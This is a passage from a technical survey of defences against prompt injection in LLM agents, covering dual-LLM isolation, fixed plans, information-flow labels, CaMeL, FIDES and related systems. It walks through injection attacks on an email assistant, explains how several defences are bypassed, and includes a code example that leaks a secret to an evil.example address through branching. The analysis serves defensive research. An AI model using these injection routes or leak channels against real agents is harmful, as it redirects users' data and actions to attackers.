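Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed the dual-LLM pattern two years before Beurer-Kellner and colleagues included it in their list. It has a privileged model with tools, a quarantined model without them, and a controller, which is ordinary software. It would handle the minutes as follows:

1. The privileged model asks for Bob's latest email. The controller fetches it, stores it as `$VAR1` and gives the privileged model only that name.
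2. The privileged model asks for the address in `$VAR1`. The controller passes the full email to the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`.
3. The privileged model asks to send the minutes to `$VAR2`. The controller fills in the real address and sends the email.

The privileged model never reads the email or the address. Willison allows one exception, for when the quarantined model only sorts text into fixed categories. The controller can then check that the answer is one of those categories and pass it to the privileged model. Free text has to stay hidden from the privileged model because a summary of a malicious email could repeat the attack.

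Willison called this solution "pretty bad". It makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and one programming mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model undoes the protection. The quarantined model's output can also deceive the user, for example with instructions to paste scrambled private data into a website.

Map-reduce is a narrower version of the same idea. For example, to email this month's invoices to the accounts department, a program runs a separate quarantined model on each file, and each model returns only yes or no. Code or another model then collects the matching files and sends them. A malicious file can still be wrongly counted as an invoice, but an attacker could achieve the same with a fake invoice. The damage is limited to this only if any model that sends the email doesn't read the files' contents.

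Code-then-execute, the approach CaMeL takes, extends the dual-LLM pattern. The planner writes a program that calls tools and quarantined models, so a request to tell all regular collaborators about a holiday can become a loop over a list of unknown length. The drawback is clearer in Beurer-Kellner and colleagues' example of an agent that answers questions from a database. If only generated code handles the query results, injected text in the database can't reach a model, but no model can check whether the results answer the question and try a different query if they don't.

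Context minimisation guards against malicious instructions in the user's prompt, which an honest user may have pasted from a web page. The model turns the request into a database query, and the program deletes the request before the model writes its reply. If a customer asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and adds an instruction to give a large discount, the instruction is no longer in the prompt when the model presents the offers. The pattern doesn't remove instructions from the query results, so it wouldn't help against any of the three attacks on the minutes.

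### The minutes under a fixed plan

Under plan-then-execute, the planner might write this before the assistant opens Bob's email:

```
email   = search_emails(sender="bob@firm.example", newest=1)
address = extract(email, "address for the minutes")
minutes = read_file("minutes/march.pdf")
send_email(to=address, attachment=minutes)
report_to_user(email, address)
```

A model extracts the address and writes the report, but it can't add steps. The three attacks then turn out differently:

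- Attack 1 fails. The planted text asks the agent to send the salary file as well, but no line reads that file or sends a second email. This depends on the plan fixing the file's path. If the executor could choose the path, the attacker might get it to send the salary file instead of the minutes.
- Attack 2 succeeds. The plan takes the address from the email, as the user asked, and the quarantined text contains the attacker's address.
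- Attack 3 succeeds, because the model that writes the report has read the false claim that Bob cancelled the April meeting.

A dual-LLM assistant could avoid attack 3 here. The privileged model could write "The minutes have gone to `$VAR2`" without reading the email, and the controller could check that `$VAR2` contains only an address. But if the user had asked for a summary of Bob's email, the false claim would still reach them.

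Beurer-Kellner and colleagues similarly conclude that a fixed plan protects the choice and order of an email assistant's actions but not the recipients or text of its emails. If the user asks the assistant to reply with whatever information the sender wants, a malicious sender could get it to look up extra confidential material and hide it in the reply as non-printing characters. Even a careful user could miss these when checking the draft.

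They nevertheless think a fixed plan would cost an email assistant little, because untrusted messages should very rarely determine which actions it takes.

### When the plan no longer fits

Many other tasks depend on what the agent finds. Xiang and colleagues give the example of a coding agent told to run a project's tests and fix any that fail. The general plan is obvious, but the next change depends on the error log, and each fix can change what fails next. A fixed plan can also fail on a simple task if a tool stops working. In their other example, a billing service has moved to a new address, and an agent that can't replan would keep calling the old one.

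The planner could prepare for some errors by including conditions in the plan, such as "if the call fails, check the documentation". Xiang and colleagues reply that nobody can list all the errors in advance, and that conditions give the attacker something to manipulate. A user might ask an agent to book a hike if tomorrow is dry and buy two cinema tickets otherwise. Anyone who can change the forecast that the agent reads can choose which of the two it does, without adding a call to the plan.

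This drawback barely shows up on AgentDojo, where only 6 of the 97 tasks need a new plan or policy, according to a count from *AgentDyn* cited by Xiang and colleagues. In a typical task, such as paying the bill in a named file, the planner can predict both the file read and the payment before it reads anything. *Trident* (2026) counts 20 of the 97 tasks as data-dependent, which means that what the agent reads can legitimately determine its next action. A defence that failed all of these tasks and did no worse on the rest would lose at most about 6 percentage points of clean utility by the first count and 21 by the second.

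Fixed plans can lose more than that when the planner is weak. A weak planner probably explains part of the 20-point drop with DRIFT's planner alone, since a stronger model than GPT-4o-mini could have planned some of those tasks correctly.

Tool Filter, a simple relative of plan-then-execute, shows the difference between benchmarks most clearly. Before the model reads any data, it selects the tools it expects to need, and the program disables the rest. In *AgentSys*'s tests on AgentDojo with GPT-4o-mini, this reduced the attack success rate from 30.7% to 8.3%, while clean utility fell only from 63.5% to 61.5%. On AgentDyn with GPT-4o, clean utility fell from 53.3% to 8.3%, because the filter disabled tools that seemed irrelevant at the start but became necessary later. GPT-4o is the stronger model, so the change of benchmark is a more likely cause of the larger drop than the change of model.

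CaMeL completed none of AgentDyn's tasks. *AgentDyn* attributes this to CaMeL's static program, although Ma and colleagues note that CaMeL also requires extensive policies for each suite. AgentDyn is also an extreme test, because every task requires replanning and includes a helpful third-party instruction, such as a request to log in before paying. Most real workloads probably fall between the two benchmarks.

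### Letting the plan change

Del Rosario and colleagues recommend running the planner again when something unexpected happens, so that the agent can recover from errors. But if the planner reads the unexpected web page or error message, an attacker who wrote it can influence the new plan. A safer design has to restrict the information the planner receives.

*ActGuard* (2026) takes a lighter approach that keeps the ordinary agent loop and plans only one step ahead. Whenever the agent proposes a call, it also predicts which tools could plausibly come next, but not their arguments, since those will depend on the call's result. If the agent then proposes a tool it didn't predict, an audit examines the call before it runs but doesn't automatically block it. The latest tool result can't influence the prediction, which the agent made before that result arrived. But text from earlier results is already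 in the agent's history and could influence both the prediction and the call.

### Placeholders: Prompt Flow Integrity

Kim, Choi and Lee (2025), in *Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents*, developed the dual-LLM idea into a system called PFI. A trusted agent plans and has full access to the tools, while an untrusted agent reads outside content with few or no tools. Untrusted results reach the trusted agent as placeholders such as #DATA0, which it can use in three ways:

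- It can pass a placeholder to a tool, and PFI fills in the real value.
- It can ask the untrusted agent a question about the content. The answer comes back as another placeholder.
- It can ask to use the content as instructions, for example when the user wants it to follow an installation guide. PFI shows the text to the user and adds it to the trusted agent's prompt only if the user approves.

The third option lets the agent replan. PFI also asks the user for approval before it puts untrusted content into a privileged tool call or the final answer. In the minutes example, the user would see the outsider's address before the email was sent and could stop attack 2. But the alert would give Bob's email as the source, because PFI traces an answer to everything the untrusted agent read rather than to a particular passage. The alert would look much the same if Bob had written a new address himself.

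Kim, Choi and Lee tested PFI with GPT-4o on a modified AgentDojo, which included planted false data as well as planted instructions. Attacks succeeded on 81.4% of tasks without a defence and on none with PFI. The undefended agent also completed 81.4% of the tasks, but only 12.4% securely. With PFI, the agent completed 61.9%, all securely.

The zero depends on counting an attack as unsuccessful whenever PFI warned the user, since the user might then refuse. If users approved alerts as readily as the testers in Anthropic's study of permission prompts, many of these attacks would succeed. PFI raised about 1.5 alerts per task, compared with 4.1 for an agent that asked about every tool call, so it interrupts users less but still often. Users can also choose to trust a source permanently. If a user did this for Bob's emails, outsiders' text that Bob forwarded could go straight into the trusted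 agent's prompt.

Kim, Choi and Lee also analysed 108 tasks that the undefended agents completed but PFI failed. In 76% of them, the trusted agent used placeholders incorrectly or asked the untrusted agent poorly formed questions. Training models to work with placeholders might prevent some of these failures, but Xiang and colleagues point out that some tasks require the hidden information itself. On AgentDojo, PFI took 63% longer than the undefended agent and used 91% more tokens.

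### Isolated memory: AgentSys

In an ordinary agent, an injection stays in the prompt after the model first reads it, so it can influence every later decision. *AgentSys* measured this in undefended AgentDojo runs of four tool calls. Injections succeeded in 60.5% of cases when they first appeared in the first round, compared with 15.4% in the second. AgentSys therefore keeps raw tool results out of the main agent's memory:

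1. With each tool call, the main agent declares which fields it wants back, such as one text field called "address".
2. A short-lived worker model reads the result and fills in the fields. It doesn't receive the user's request or the main agent's history.
3. Code checks that the answer is valid JSON, a standard format for structured data. The main agent receives the answer, and the program discards the worker's memory.
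4. If the worker needs another tool that could change something, a validator model compares the call with the user's request and the earlier calls, without reading any tool results. If the validator refuses, a sanitiser removes instructions from the tool result and the worker tries again, up to a fixed limit.

The main agent chooses each step after it receives the previous answer, so it can change its plan. The results below are for AgentDojo with GPT-4o-mini:

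| Version | Clean utility | Utility under attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 63.5% | 48.3% | 30.7% |
| Full AgentSys | 64.4% | 52.9% | 0.8% |
| Isolated workers only | 56.1% | 52.6% | 2.2% |
| Validator and sanitiser only | 62.5% | 50.2% | 8.6% |

Isolation provides most of the security, and the other two parts recover the clean utility that isolation loses. The full system used about four times as many tokens as the undefended agent. AgentDojo tasks rarely require replanning, so these results provide little evidence of how well AgentSys handles tasks that do.

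AgentSys relaxes the principle behind the six patterns, because its main agent reads values that an attacker may have written. The JSON check verifies only the format, so a worker could return a name followed by an instruction, or add a field that nobody requested. The validator doesn't check the main agent's own calls, so if the main agent follows an injected instruction, no later check will stop it. Such attacks are difficult in practice. An automated attacker that repeatedly revised its text succeeded in 2.1% of cases overall and 6.9% in the banking suite.

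In the minutes example, the outsider would have to fit attack 1 or attack 3 into the reply to a request for an address. Attack 2 only requires the reply to contain the attacker's address, which is a valid answer.

### Limiting what the planner can learn

*Trident* further restricts the channel by measuring how much information passes through it. The planner can query a separate model about untrusted text, but it receives only answers from a fixed list, with placeholders replacing everything else.

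A reference monitor counts each answer against a budget. A question with n possible answers uses log₂ n bits, so a yes-or-no answer uses one bit and a choice among eight options uses three. A second budget covers signals that an attacker could trigger deliberately, such as a failed query or a blocked call. If the trusted inputs and the models' randomness stay the same, budgets of β and σ bits limit an attacker to a choice of at most 2^(β + σ) observable sequences of events, or 1,024 when the budgets total ten bits.

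The budget limits the number of courses of action but not the harm any one of them can do. For example, a single bit can decide whether the agent makes a payment. Trident therefore also needs policies, which a third model writes without reading any untrusted text.

Suppose a user's manager has forwarded a caterer's email, and the user asks the agent to carry out the request in it and pay from the team account. Before the agent reads the email, the policy model selects a rule that permits one payment of up to $5,000 to an account in the company's vendor records. The planner learns that the email contains an invoice, looks up the caterer and pays. If an attacker has added new bank details to the email, they have no effect, because the account number has to come from the vendor records. But no trusted record contains the amount, so the attacker could still inflate the bill to as much as $5,000.

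For the minutes, a rule requiring the address to come from the company directory would work like the CONTACTS rule, except that the user could approve Bob's new address.

Trident's developers tested it on ReplanInject, their own benchmark of 45 tasks. Depending on the model, it completed 54% to 74% of the tasks under attack, and on average it did better than CaMeL, Progent and the other defences in the comparison. With a person reviewing doubtful calls, none of the attacks tested succeeded. Trident was designed for tasks of this kind, so its advantage could be smaller on others.

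User requests differ in how much they leave for the untrusted text to determine. The caterer request specifies whose email it is, what it concerns and which account to pay from, which is enough to write useful rules before the agent reads the email. "Do what Jane's email says" specifies only where to find the instructions. *Trident* concedes that no policy can always distinguish the user's intent from the attacker's in that case, so the agent has to ask the user what they want it to do.

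## Tracking where each piece of data came from

In attack 2, the outsider's address looks normal. It differs from Bob's real address only in who wrote it, and an ordinary agent has no reliable record of that when it calls the mail tool. Information-flow control, a technique from the 1970s, keeps such a record. Software attaches a label to each piece of data when it arrives, works out a label for everything derived from it, and checks the labels before any tool call that could do harm.

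### Labels and how they combine

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses two kinds of label. An integrity label records how far data is trusted, in its simplest form as either T (trusted) or U (untrusted). A confidentiality label records who may see the data and can be a list of permitted readers.

Anything derived from several inputs takes the most restrictive combination of their labels. Computer scientists call this combination the join and write it ⊔. For integrity, one untrusted input makes the result untrusted:

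T ⊔ T = T, but T ⊔ U = U.

For confidentiality, only people who may read every input may read the result:

{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {B, C}.

Before a consequential call, meaning one that changes something or sends data out, code can then apply two policies:

- Trusted action: the call may run only if the choice of tool, and each argument that matters, has the label T.
- Permitted flow: data may go only to people on its list of readers.

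The permitted flow policy alone doesn't stop an injection from steering the agent, but it limits where private data can end up. Under both policies, the agent can send an email only if the decision to send it was based on trusted data and the recipients are allowed to read its contents.

Labels can also name particular sources. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) describes a system that records which sources have influenced each piece of data. If an agent reads a page from phony.com and then tries to write to a place that accepts only the user's own data, the program stops with an error.

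### How one email taints the whole context

A model's output is hard to label because software can't reliably tell which parts of the prompt influenced it. The safe assumption is that all of them did. In the minutes example, the context starts with the user's request, which is trusted and readable by anyone.

1. The agent reads Bob's email, which has the label U and the readers {user, Bob}. The context becomes T ⊔ U = U, with the readers {user, Bob}.
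2. The agent reads the March minutes, a trusted file that all staff may read. The context stays at U ⊔ T = U, and its readers are still {user, Bob}, since both are staff.
3. The model proposes an email. The choice of tool, the recipient and the attachment all come from this context, so each of them has the label U.

The trusted-action policy blocks the email, which stops attacks 1 and 2, but it would block the same email if no outsider had written to Bob. It would even block sending the minutes to an address the user had typed in the request, because the model copied that address after reading Bob's email. Reading more trusted files wouldn't change this, since a join never turns U back into T.

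In Costa and colleagues' tests on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, adding labels and policy checks to an ordinary agent cut the share of clean tasks it completed from 98.8% to 37.5% in the banking suite and from 93.3% to 20.0% in the Slack suite.

One remedy is to look for a smaller set of messages that leads to nearly the same answer, regenerate the answer from those alone, and give it only their labels. Another is to keep the untrusted text out of the planner's context.

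### FIDES

FIDES, a planner that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, takes the second approach. It hides text in variables, as the dual-LLM pattern does, but only when showing the text would make the context's label more restrictive. It would handle the minutes like this:

1. The mail tool returns Bob's message with a label on each field. The sender's address can stay visible if the mail server has authenticated it. The subject and body are untrusted, so code moves them into variables and shows the planner only the variables' names.
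2. The planner asks a quarantined model to find the address in the body. The answer goes into a new variable with the label U.
3. The planner fetches the minutes and proposes an email to the address in that variable.
4. Code fills in the real address and checks the labels. The decision to send the email has the label T, because the planner has seen only trusted data. The recipient has the label U.

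Each part of the call now has its own label, so the policy can treat the parts differently. It might require a trusted recipient but allow untrusted text in the body of the email, which is enough for tasks like sending a colleague the results of a web search. If the policy checks only the decision to send, attack 2 succeeds.

Sometimes the planner needs the contents of a variable. It can open the variable, but its context then becomes untrusted and later calls may fail the policy. FIDES offers a less drastic option. Suppose the user asks for a calendar event if any recent email requests a meeting. The planner can ask the quarantined model whether any email does, and the decoding software blocks every output except yes or no. The label on the answer records both its type and its origin. A policy can then let an untrusted yes or no influence the next action while refusing an untrusted string,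 because the attacker controls at most one bit of the answer.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) object in *The LLMbda Calculus* that such exceptions are hard to audit. When the policy lets a small value through, a reviewer can't tell from that run whether this was the harmless exception the designers intended or a real leak.

The table gives the share of clean AgentDojo tasks completed with GPT-4o. These tests did not enforce answer types in the decoding software.

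| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, labels and checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, no checks | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

With checks on, FIDES's average task completion rate was about 8 percentage points higher than the ordinary agent's. The exception was the travel suite, where many tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context. The checks therefore didn't lower the ordinary agent's score there, while GPT-4o often misused FIDES's variables. OpenAI's reasoning model o1 handled the variables better and raised FIDES's travel score from 41% to 68%.

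Some tasks failed because the policy worked as intended. In about 43% of the banking and Slack tasks, the right action depends on what the agent reads, as when the user tells it to follow the instructions in a file. One success was also less impressive than it looks, because the agent never opened the transaction's hidden description. The user had asked it to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction, and it judged by the amount, which was trusted. The context therefore stayed trusted, and the policy allowed the change.

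AgentDojo's strongest standard attack succeeded 152 times against the ordinary agent without checks and 21 times against FIDES without checks. It never succeeded when the checks were on. Costa and colleagues excluded cases that they thought AgentDojo had misclassified.

They marked as untrusted every field that some AgentDojo attack targets, so no attack could arrive through a mislabelled field. Their test policies also didn't check arguments. The zero result is therefore good evidence that the defence stops attack 1, but little evidence that it stops attack 2.

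### CaMeL

CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, also combines labels with a planner that doesn't see untrusted text, but its planner writes the whole plan as a program before any tool runs. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe the design in detail because their own system adds a check on that program before it starts. For the minutes, the plan might be:

```
email   = search_emails(sender="bob@firm.example", newest=1)
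address = ask_quarantined(f"Address for the minutes: {email}",
                          EmailAddress)
minutes = read_file("minutes/march.pdf")
send_email(to=address, attachment=minutes)
```

The language is a restricted form of Python, without features such as `while` loops. CaMeL's own interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls. When it reaches the second line, it passes the email to a quarantined model, which must return an email address. An injection in the email can change the value of `address` but can't add a line to the program.

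The interpreter tags every value with its sources and its permitted readers. CaMeL's developers call these tags capabilities. In the example they might be:

| Value | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| `"minutes/march.pdf"` | The user's request | Anyone |
| `email` | Bob's message, through the mail tool | User and Bob |
| `address` | Bob's message, through the quarantined model | User and Bob |
| `minutes` | The company's file store | All staff |

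Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy function, which is ordinary Python that someone has written for that tool. It receives the arguments with their tags and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason. A strict one for email might be:

```
def email_policy(to, attachment):
    if not from_trusted_source(to):
        return deny("recipient came from untrusted text")
    if not may_read(to, attachment):
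        return deny("recipient may not read this file")
    return allow()
```

Attack 1 fails, as it does under any fixed plan that names the file. Attack 2 fails the policy's first test because the outsider's address came from an email. But Bob's genuine new address came from the same email through the same quarantined model, so it has the same tags and also fails. Even his old address would fail if the program took it from the message instead of the company directory. The user gets a refusal whether the address is Bob's or the outsider's, until someone or something confirms it.

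Attack 3 is outside CaMeL's scope, as Narisetty and colleagues note. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), which enforces similar rules through a programming language's type system, gives an example from AgentDojo. The user asked the agent to book a hotel, and an attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews in its reply. The policy allowed this because public reviews may flow to the user. A stricter policy could check replies too, but it would help little when the user has asked for a summary of an untrusted email.

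### What CaMeL costs

Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL, using OpenAI's o3 model, completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. No injection within CaMeL's threat model succeeded.

The loss is larger in other conditions. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, report a clean utility of 53.6% for CaMeL with GPT-4o and 83.0% for their own undefended agent. They took the CaMeL figure from CaMeL's published results because they couldn't fully reproduce those results. Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL's policy checks halve its utility in the banking suite, so a CaMeL score means little unless the source states whether the checks were on.

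The same paper suggests that labels may not have to reduce utility this much. An agent built in the paper's own language, with label checks always on, roughly matched the banking utility of CaMeL without checks and resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* also reports utility close to CaMeL's, using a single ordinary agent loop instead of a separate planner and executor.

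Bhagwatkar and colleagues state that CaMeL uses 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent on the median AgentDojo task, with GPT-4o and without counting tool descriptions. Their own token counts don't match this. The medians give ratios of 1.8 for input and 2.2 for output, while the means give 3.6 and 6.1. "About three times the input" is a fair summary, but a few long tasks probably account for much of the extra token use.

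Their sanitiser, a model that rewrites each tool result without the injected text, also reduced attack success to zero on the same static attacks and kept a clean utility of 74.1%. This doesn't make it as secure as CaMeL, which has a stronger guarantee, but static attacks that both defences stop can't show whether that guarantee is worth its drawbacks.

CaMeL does worst when nobody can write the program in advance. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) measured CaMeL's utility at 31.0% on a benchmark that combines AgentDojo's four suites with AgentDyn's three. CaMeL again completed no tasks in the AgentDyn suites.

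### Vouching for data

A system with strict labels needs a way to make exceptions. Endorsement raises the integrity of a piece of data from untrusted (U) to trusted (T). If the user checks the new address with Bob and confirms it, the program can relabel the address as trusted and send the minutes. Declassification relaxes confidentiality by adding readers. If only staff may read the minutes, someone has to declassify them before the user can share them with an outside auditor.

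Trust labels and secrecy labels should stay separate, so that vouching for Bob's address doesn't make the salary file public. Garby and colleagues designed their endorsement command so that changing one kind of label leaves the guarantees for the other intact. The command also appears explicitly in the program, so a reviewer can find every exception.

A policy can sometimes infer a declassification. If the planner decided to send a file while its context was still trusted, no untrusted text influenced that decision, so the system may assume the user intended to share the file. Costa and colleagues note that dropping the permitted-flow rule for trusted decisions amounts to inferring declassification in this way. The assumption is weaker when the model has misunderstood the request.

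The effect of an endorsement depends on how much data it covers. Endorsing one address lets only that value through, but endorsing the whole of Bob's email would also relabel the outsider's forwarded text as trusted. The planner could then read that text and obey it while its context was still labelled trusted.

### Planning for fewer approvals

FIDES's planner doesn't know the policies it has to satisfy. It may open a variable it didn't need and then run into refusals for the rest of the task. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, built a planner called Prudentia on top of FIDES to avoid this. It differs in three ways:

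- Each tool's description states its policy, and the planner can see the label of its own context.
- Before opening a variable, the planner has to explain why it needs the contents and list the calls it expects to make afterwards.
- When it opens a variable, it can ask the user to endorse the contents, or it can accept an untrusted context and ask for approval of later calls.

The best choice depends on the task. Suppose an email contains a to-do list with ten items, each requiring a consequential call. Endorsing the email takes one question, while approving the calls takes ten. If the agent only has to read the email and report back, it needs no endorsement. Kolluri and colleagues left out declassification because whether to release private data depends on the recipient and purpose, which are clearer in a question about a single call.

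They argue that earlier comparisons were unfair to label-based defences, since an undefended agent in real use would ask a person to approve each consequential call. They therefore count approvals. If v_i is the number of calls in task i that would need a person's approval, the completion rate with at most k approvals per task is

TCR@k = (number of completed tasks with v_i ≤ k) / (number of tasks).

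On AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini and no approvals allowed, the results were:

| Agent | Tasks completed without any approval |
|---|---|
| Ordinary agent that asks before every consequential call | 24.3% |
| Ordinary agent with labels | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | 59.1% |

With o4-mini and unlimited approvals, Prudentia completed 73.2% of tasks and needed 19.2 approvals in total, while FIDES completed 75.7% and needed 36.8. Prudentia therefore needed roughly one approval for every four completed tasks, and FIDES needed one for every two. On WASP, a benchmark for web-browsing agents, Prudentia needed no approvals and no attack succeeded. But the user only asked the agent to post a comment or upvote a post, so it never had to read the untrusted text.

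These counts assume that the user answers every question correctly. Fewer questions should help, given how rarely testers rejected dangerous commands in Anthropic's study of permission prompts. But one endorsement can cover several calls. If an attacker adds an eleventh item to the to-do list, a user who endorses the email without reading to the end approves that item too. If the system asked about each call separately, the user would at least see the added call on its own.

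### Letting the request decide whom to trust

Users often say whom they trust without being asked. "Send it to the address in Bob's latest email" authorises Bob to supply the address. Ma, Xiao and colleagues (2026), in *ROPE*, turn such statements into rules:

1. Before deployment, a model lists the sensitive parameters of each tool, such as the recipient of an email, and gives each a default rule. People review the list.
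2. For each task, another model reads the user's request and other trusted information, but no tool results. It decides which sources may supply each sensitive value.
3. While the agent works, code records where each text came from. It accepts three kinds of source: the user's request, messages from an authenticated sender whom the user named, and protected fields in the user's own records.
4. Before a call that changes something, code checks that each guarded value appears in full in a text from a permitted source. If the text contains "notevil.com", for example, that doesn't permit "evil.com".

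The agent can change its plan and read everything, because the check applies only to the values it finally uses. In one test, the user asked the agent to summarise a document that Lily had shared by email and send her the summary. DRIFT had guessed Lily's address before reading anything, so it refused the real one. PFI, which hides addresses behind placeholders, sent the summary to the user. ROPE found the address in an authenticated message from Lily and allowed the agent to use it.

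On AgentDyn with GPT-4o-mini, ROPE completed 36.7% of clean tasks, compared with 46.7% without a defence, 18.3% for DRIFT, 15.0% for PFI and 6.7% for Progent. Static attacks succeeded against ROPE 0.3% of the time. ROPE also did better on requests like the one for the minutes, which specify the action but leave a value to outside content. Averaged over four models, it completed 44.2% of these, compared with 24.2% for DRIFT. A much stronger model, Claude Opus 4.8, wrote ROPE's rules in these tests.

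ROPE would admit Bob's new address without asking the user if Bob wrote it himself. It would also admit the outsider's address if Bob forwarded it, because code labels each message by its authenticated sender without checking who wrote the text inside. Ma and colleagues prove that no value found only in attacker-written text can reach a guarded parameter, but the proof assumes that the named sender wrote the whole message, which is false when the message contains forwarded text.

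The rule also blocks some legitimate actions when nobody is attacking. ROPE treats an unsigned file or web page as untrusted even if the user named it, so it can't take an account number from "the bill in this file". It also rejects a value that the agent correctly worked out from trusted data if the value itself doesn't appear in that data.

### Wrong labels at the start

Every label depends on a decision about where data enters the system. Narisetty and colleagues found that none of the systems they surveyed fully specified this decision. For example, most systems trust whatever the user types, but users paste in text from web pages and emails. The deployed version of FIDES treats data as trusted if a developer forgot to label it. Treating unlabelled data as untrusted would be safer, but a forgotten label would then break legitimate tasks.

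Some systems might relabel a document from untrusted (U) to trusted (T) after an injection classifier has passed it. Costa and colleagues mention this option with a warning. Any injection the classifier missed would then enter the planner's context with a trusted label, and the policy would consistently treat it as trusted.

Fine labels are harder to get right than coarse ones. U is the only safe label for the whole body of Bob's email unless the mail tool stores a forwarded message as a separate item with its own verified sender.

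### Leaks through branches and timing

Labels follow data as a program copies it, but a program can also reveal a secret through its actions. Suppose an agent emails a caterer only if a confidential guest list has more than 50 names. Even if the email contains nothing from the list, the caterer can learn something about the list from receiving it. FIDES doesn't prevent this. It guarantees what Costa and colleagues call explicit secrecy, which covers the data in each call but not what an observer can infer from which calls the agent makes. Preventing such leaks completely would mean forbidding almost all publicly visible calls after the agent had read a secret, which they consider too restrictive.

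CaMeL goes further and also labels actions inside a branch that depends on a secret. Garby and colleagues found that the branch a program doesn't take can still leak. A simplified version of their example is:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > limit: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the limit, the third line sets `tmp` to false and gives it a secret label. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` keeps its original public label, and the policy lets the last line send the email. If the balance is below the limit, `rich` becomes false and no email is sent. The attacker therefore learns whether the balance is above the limit, even though the label on `rich` was public throughout.

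CaMeL has another leak outside the interpreter. It restarts a failed program in a loop that the labels don't cover, and whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret. Most label systems tolerate the one bit that a single attempt reveals, but repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret. Twenty bits are enough to identify any six-digit code.

Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, list further channels: the number of times a loop runs, whether an error occurs, and how long an operation takes. They suggest capping loops that depend on secrets, handling errors and successes in the same way, and padding sensitive operations to a fixed duration. Padding slows the agent, and blocking calls inside secret-dependent loops would stop some legitimate tasks.

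For most agents, these leaks are a smaller worry than a wrong label because they reveal data but don't let an outsider choose where the minutes are sent. Planted text also doesn't reach CaMeL's planner, so an attacker would need to get the user to paste in a malicious request or find a plan that already branches on a secret.

### Labels lost in a summary

In long tasks, unlike AgentDojo's short ones, the prompt can approach the model's length limit. The agent's program then has a model summarise the earlier conversation and continues from the summary. Each original message had a role, such as user or tool, but the summary combines their content into one text. The join rule would label the summary untrusted if it covered even one untrusted email, and every later call would inherit that label.

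Current agents tend to lose track of where data came from when they summarise a conversation. Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, recorded 1,108 automatic summaries in Claude Code and Codex, and in every case the program inserted the summary as a user message. A defence that derives its policy from the user's latest message may then treat the summary as the user's request. Dabirsiaghi (2026), in *Compaction Laundering*, found that coding agents usually lose track of who wrote what if they flatten the conversation into plain text before summarising it, but not if they keep roles in separate fields.

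Fei and colleagues tested the effect on Progent, modified to write a new policy for each request. In one scenario, the user had already said which account to pay the rent to, and a planted notice gave a different account as plain information. After a frontier model summarised the conversation, the new policy allowed payment to the attacker's account in 91% of cases with one policy-writing model and 59% with another. The policy never allowed this when it was written from the user's own words. The summarising models often flagged planted commands but rarely planted facts.

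A better summariser can't fully solve this. Let p_L be the chance that a policy accepts a value from a legitimate record, and p_A the chance that it accepts one from a forged record. Fei and colleagues prove that, for any system that sees only the text and not who wrote it,

p_L − p_A ≤ D,

where D measures how far the two kinds of text can be told apart, from 0 (not at all) to 1 (perfectly). If the attacker copies the format of real records exactly, D is 0, and the system has to accept forgeries as often as genuine records.

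The remedy gives the agent and the policy writer different inputs. The agent continues from the summary, while the policy writer receives only the user's own messages, word for word, each with a cryptographic tag added on arrival. Code also checks that no message is missing or out of order. If any check fails, the new policy permits nothing, so an attacker may be able to halt the agent but can't influence what the policy allows. In 40 attacked AgentDojo runs with this protection, no attacker's action went through.

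In the minutes example, this would preserve the instruction to use the address in Bob's email, but the user never typed the address itself. To determine who supplied the address, the program would still need to keep the label on Bob's email or reread the email after the summary.

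## What has been proved about fixed plans and monitors

When ordinary code runs a fixed plan under a reference monitor, researchers can prove statements about all attacks of a given kind, even if the model obeys every injected instruction. Testing cannot do the same, because nobody can test every wording of an attack. The value of such a proof depends on its definition of security and its assumptions about the system.

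### Why the classical definition is too strict

A system satisfies noninterference, the classical definition of leaking nothing, if what an attacker observes does not depend on the user's secrets. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that answers meeting requests with the user's free times. Its replies depend on the user's calendar, so it violates noninterference even when every request is genuine. Declassification rules can allow such replies, but someone has to write a separate rule for each task.

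Another simple definition, which counts an agent as insecure whenever its model obeys an injected instruction, would be too strict. If a stranger's email orders the assistant to send the user's free times and the assistant obeys, the stranger learns only what an honest meeting request would have told them.

### Relative security

Dongol instead compares the LLM agent with an imaginary reference agent. Both run the same plan under the same monitor, but the reference agent's model never obeys untrusted text. Take two runs of an agent in which the attacker writes the same text but the user's secrets are σ₁ in one run and σ₂ in the other. If the attacker sees different things in the two runs, the agent leaks the difference between σ₁ and σ₂. The LLM agent is relatively secure if, for all σ₁ and σ₂,

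LLM agent leaks (σ₁, σ₂) ⇒ reference agent leaks (σ₁, σ₂).

The attacker may send the reference agent a different text. The definition therefore allows the injected request for free times, because an honest meeting request gets the same information from the reference agent. If the injection adds "also include the password reset code", the agent is no longer relatively secure, because no email gets that code from the reference agent.

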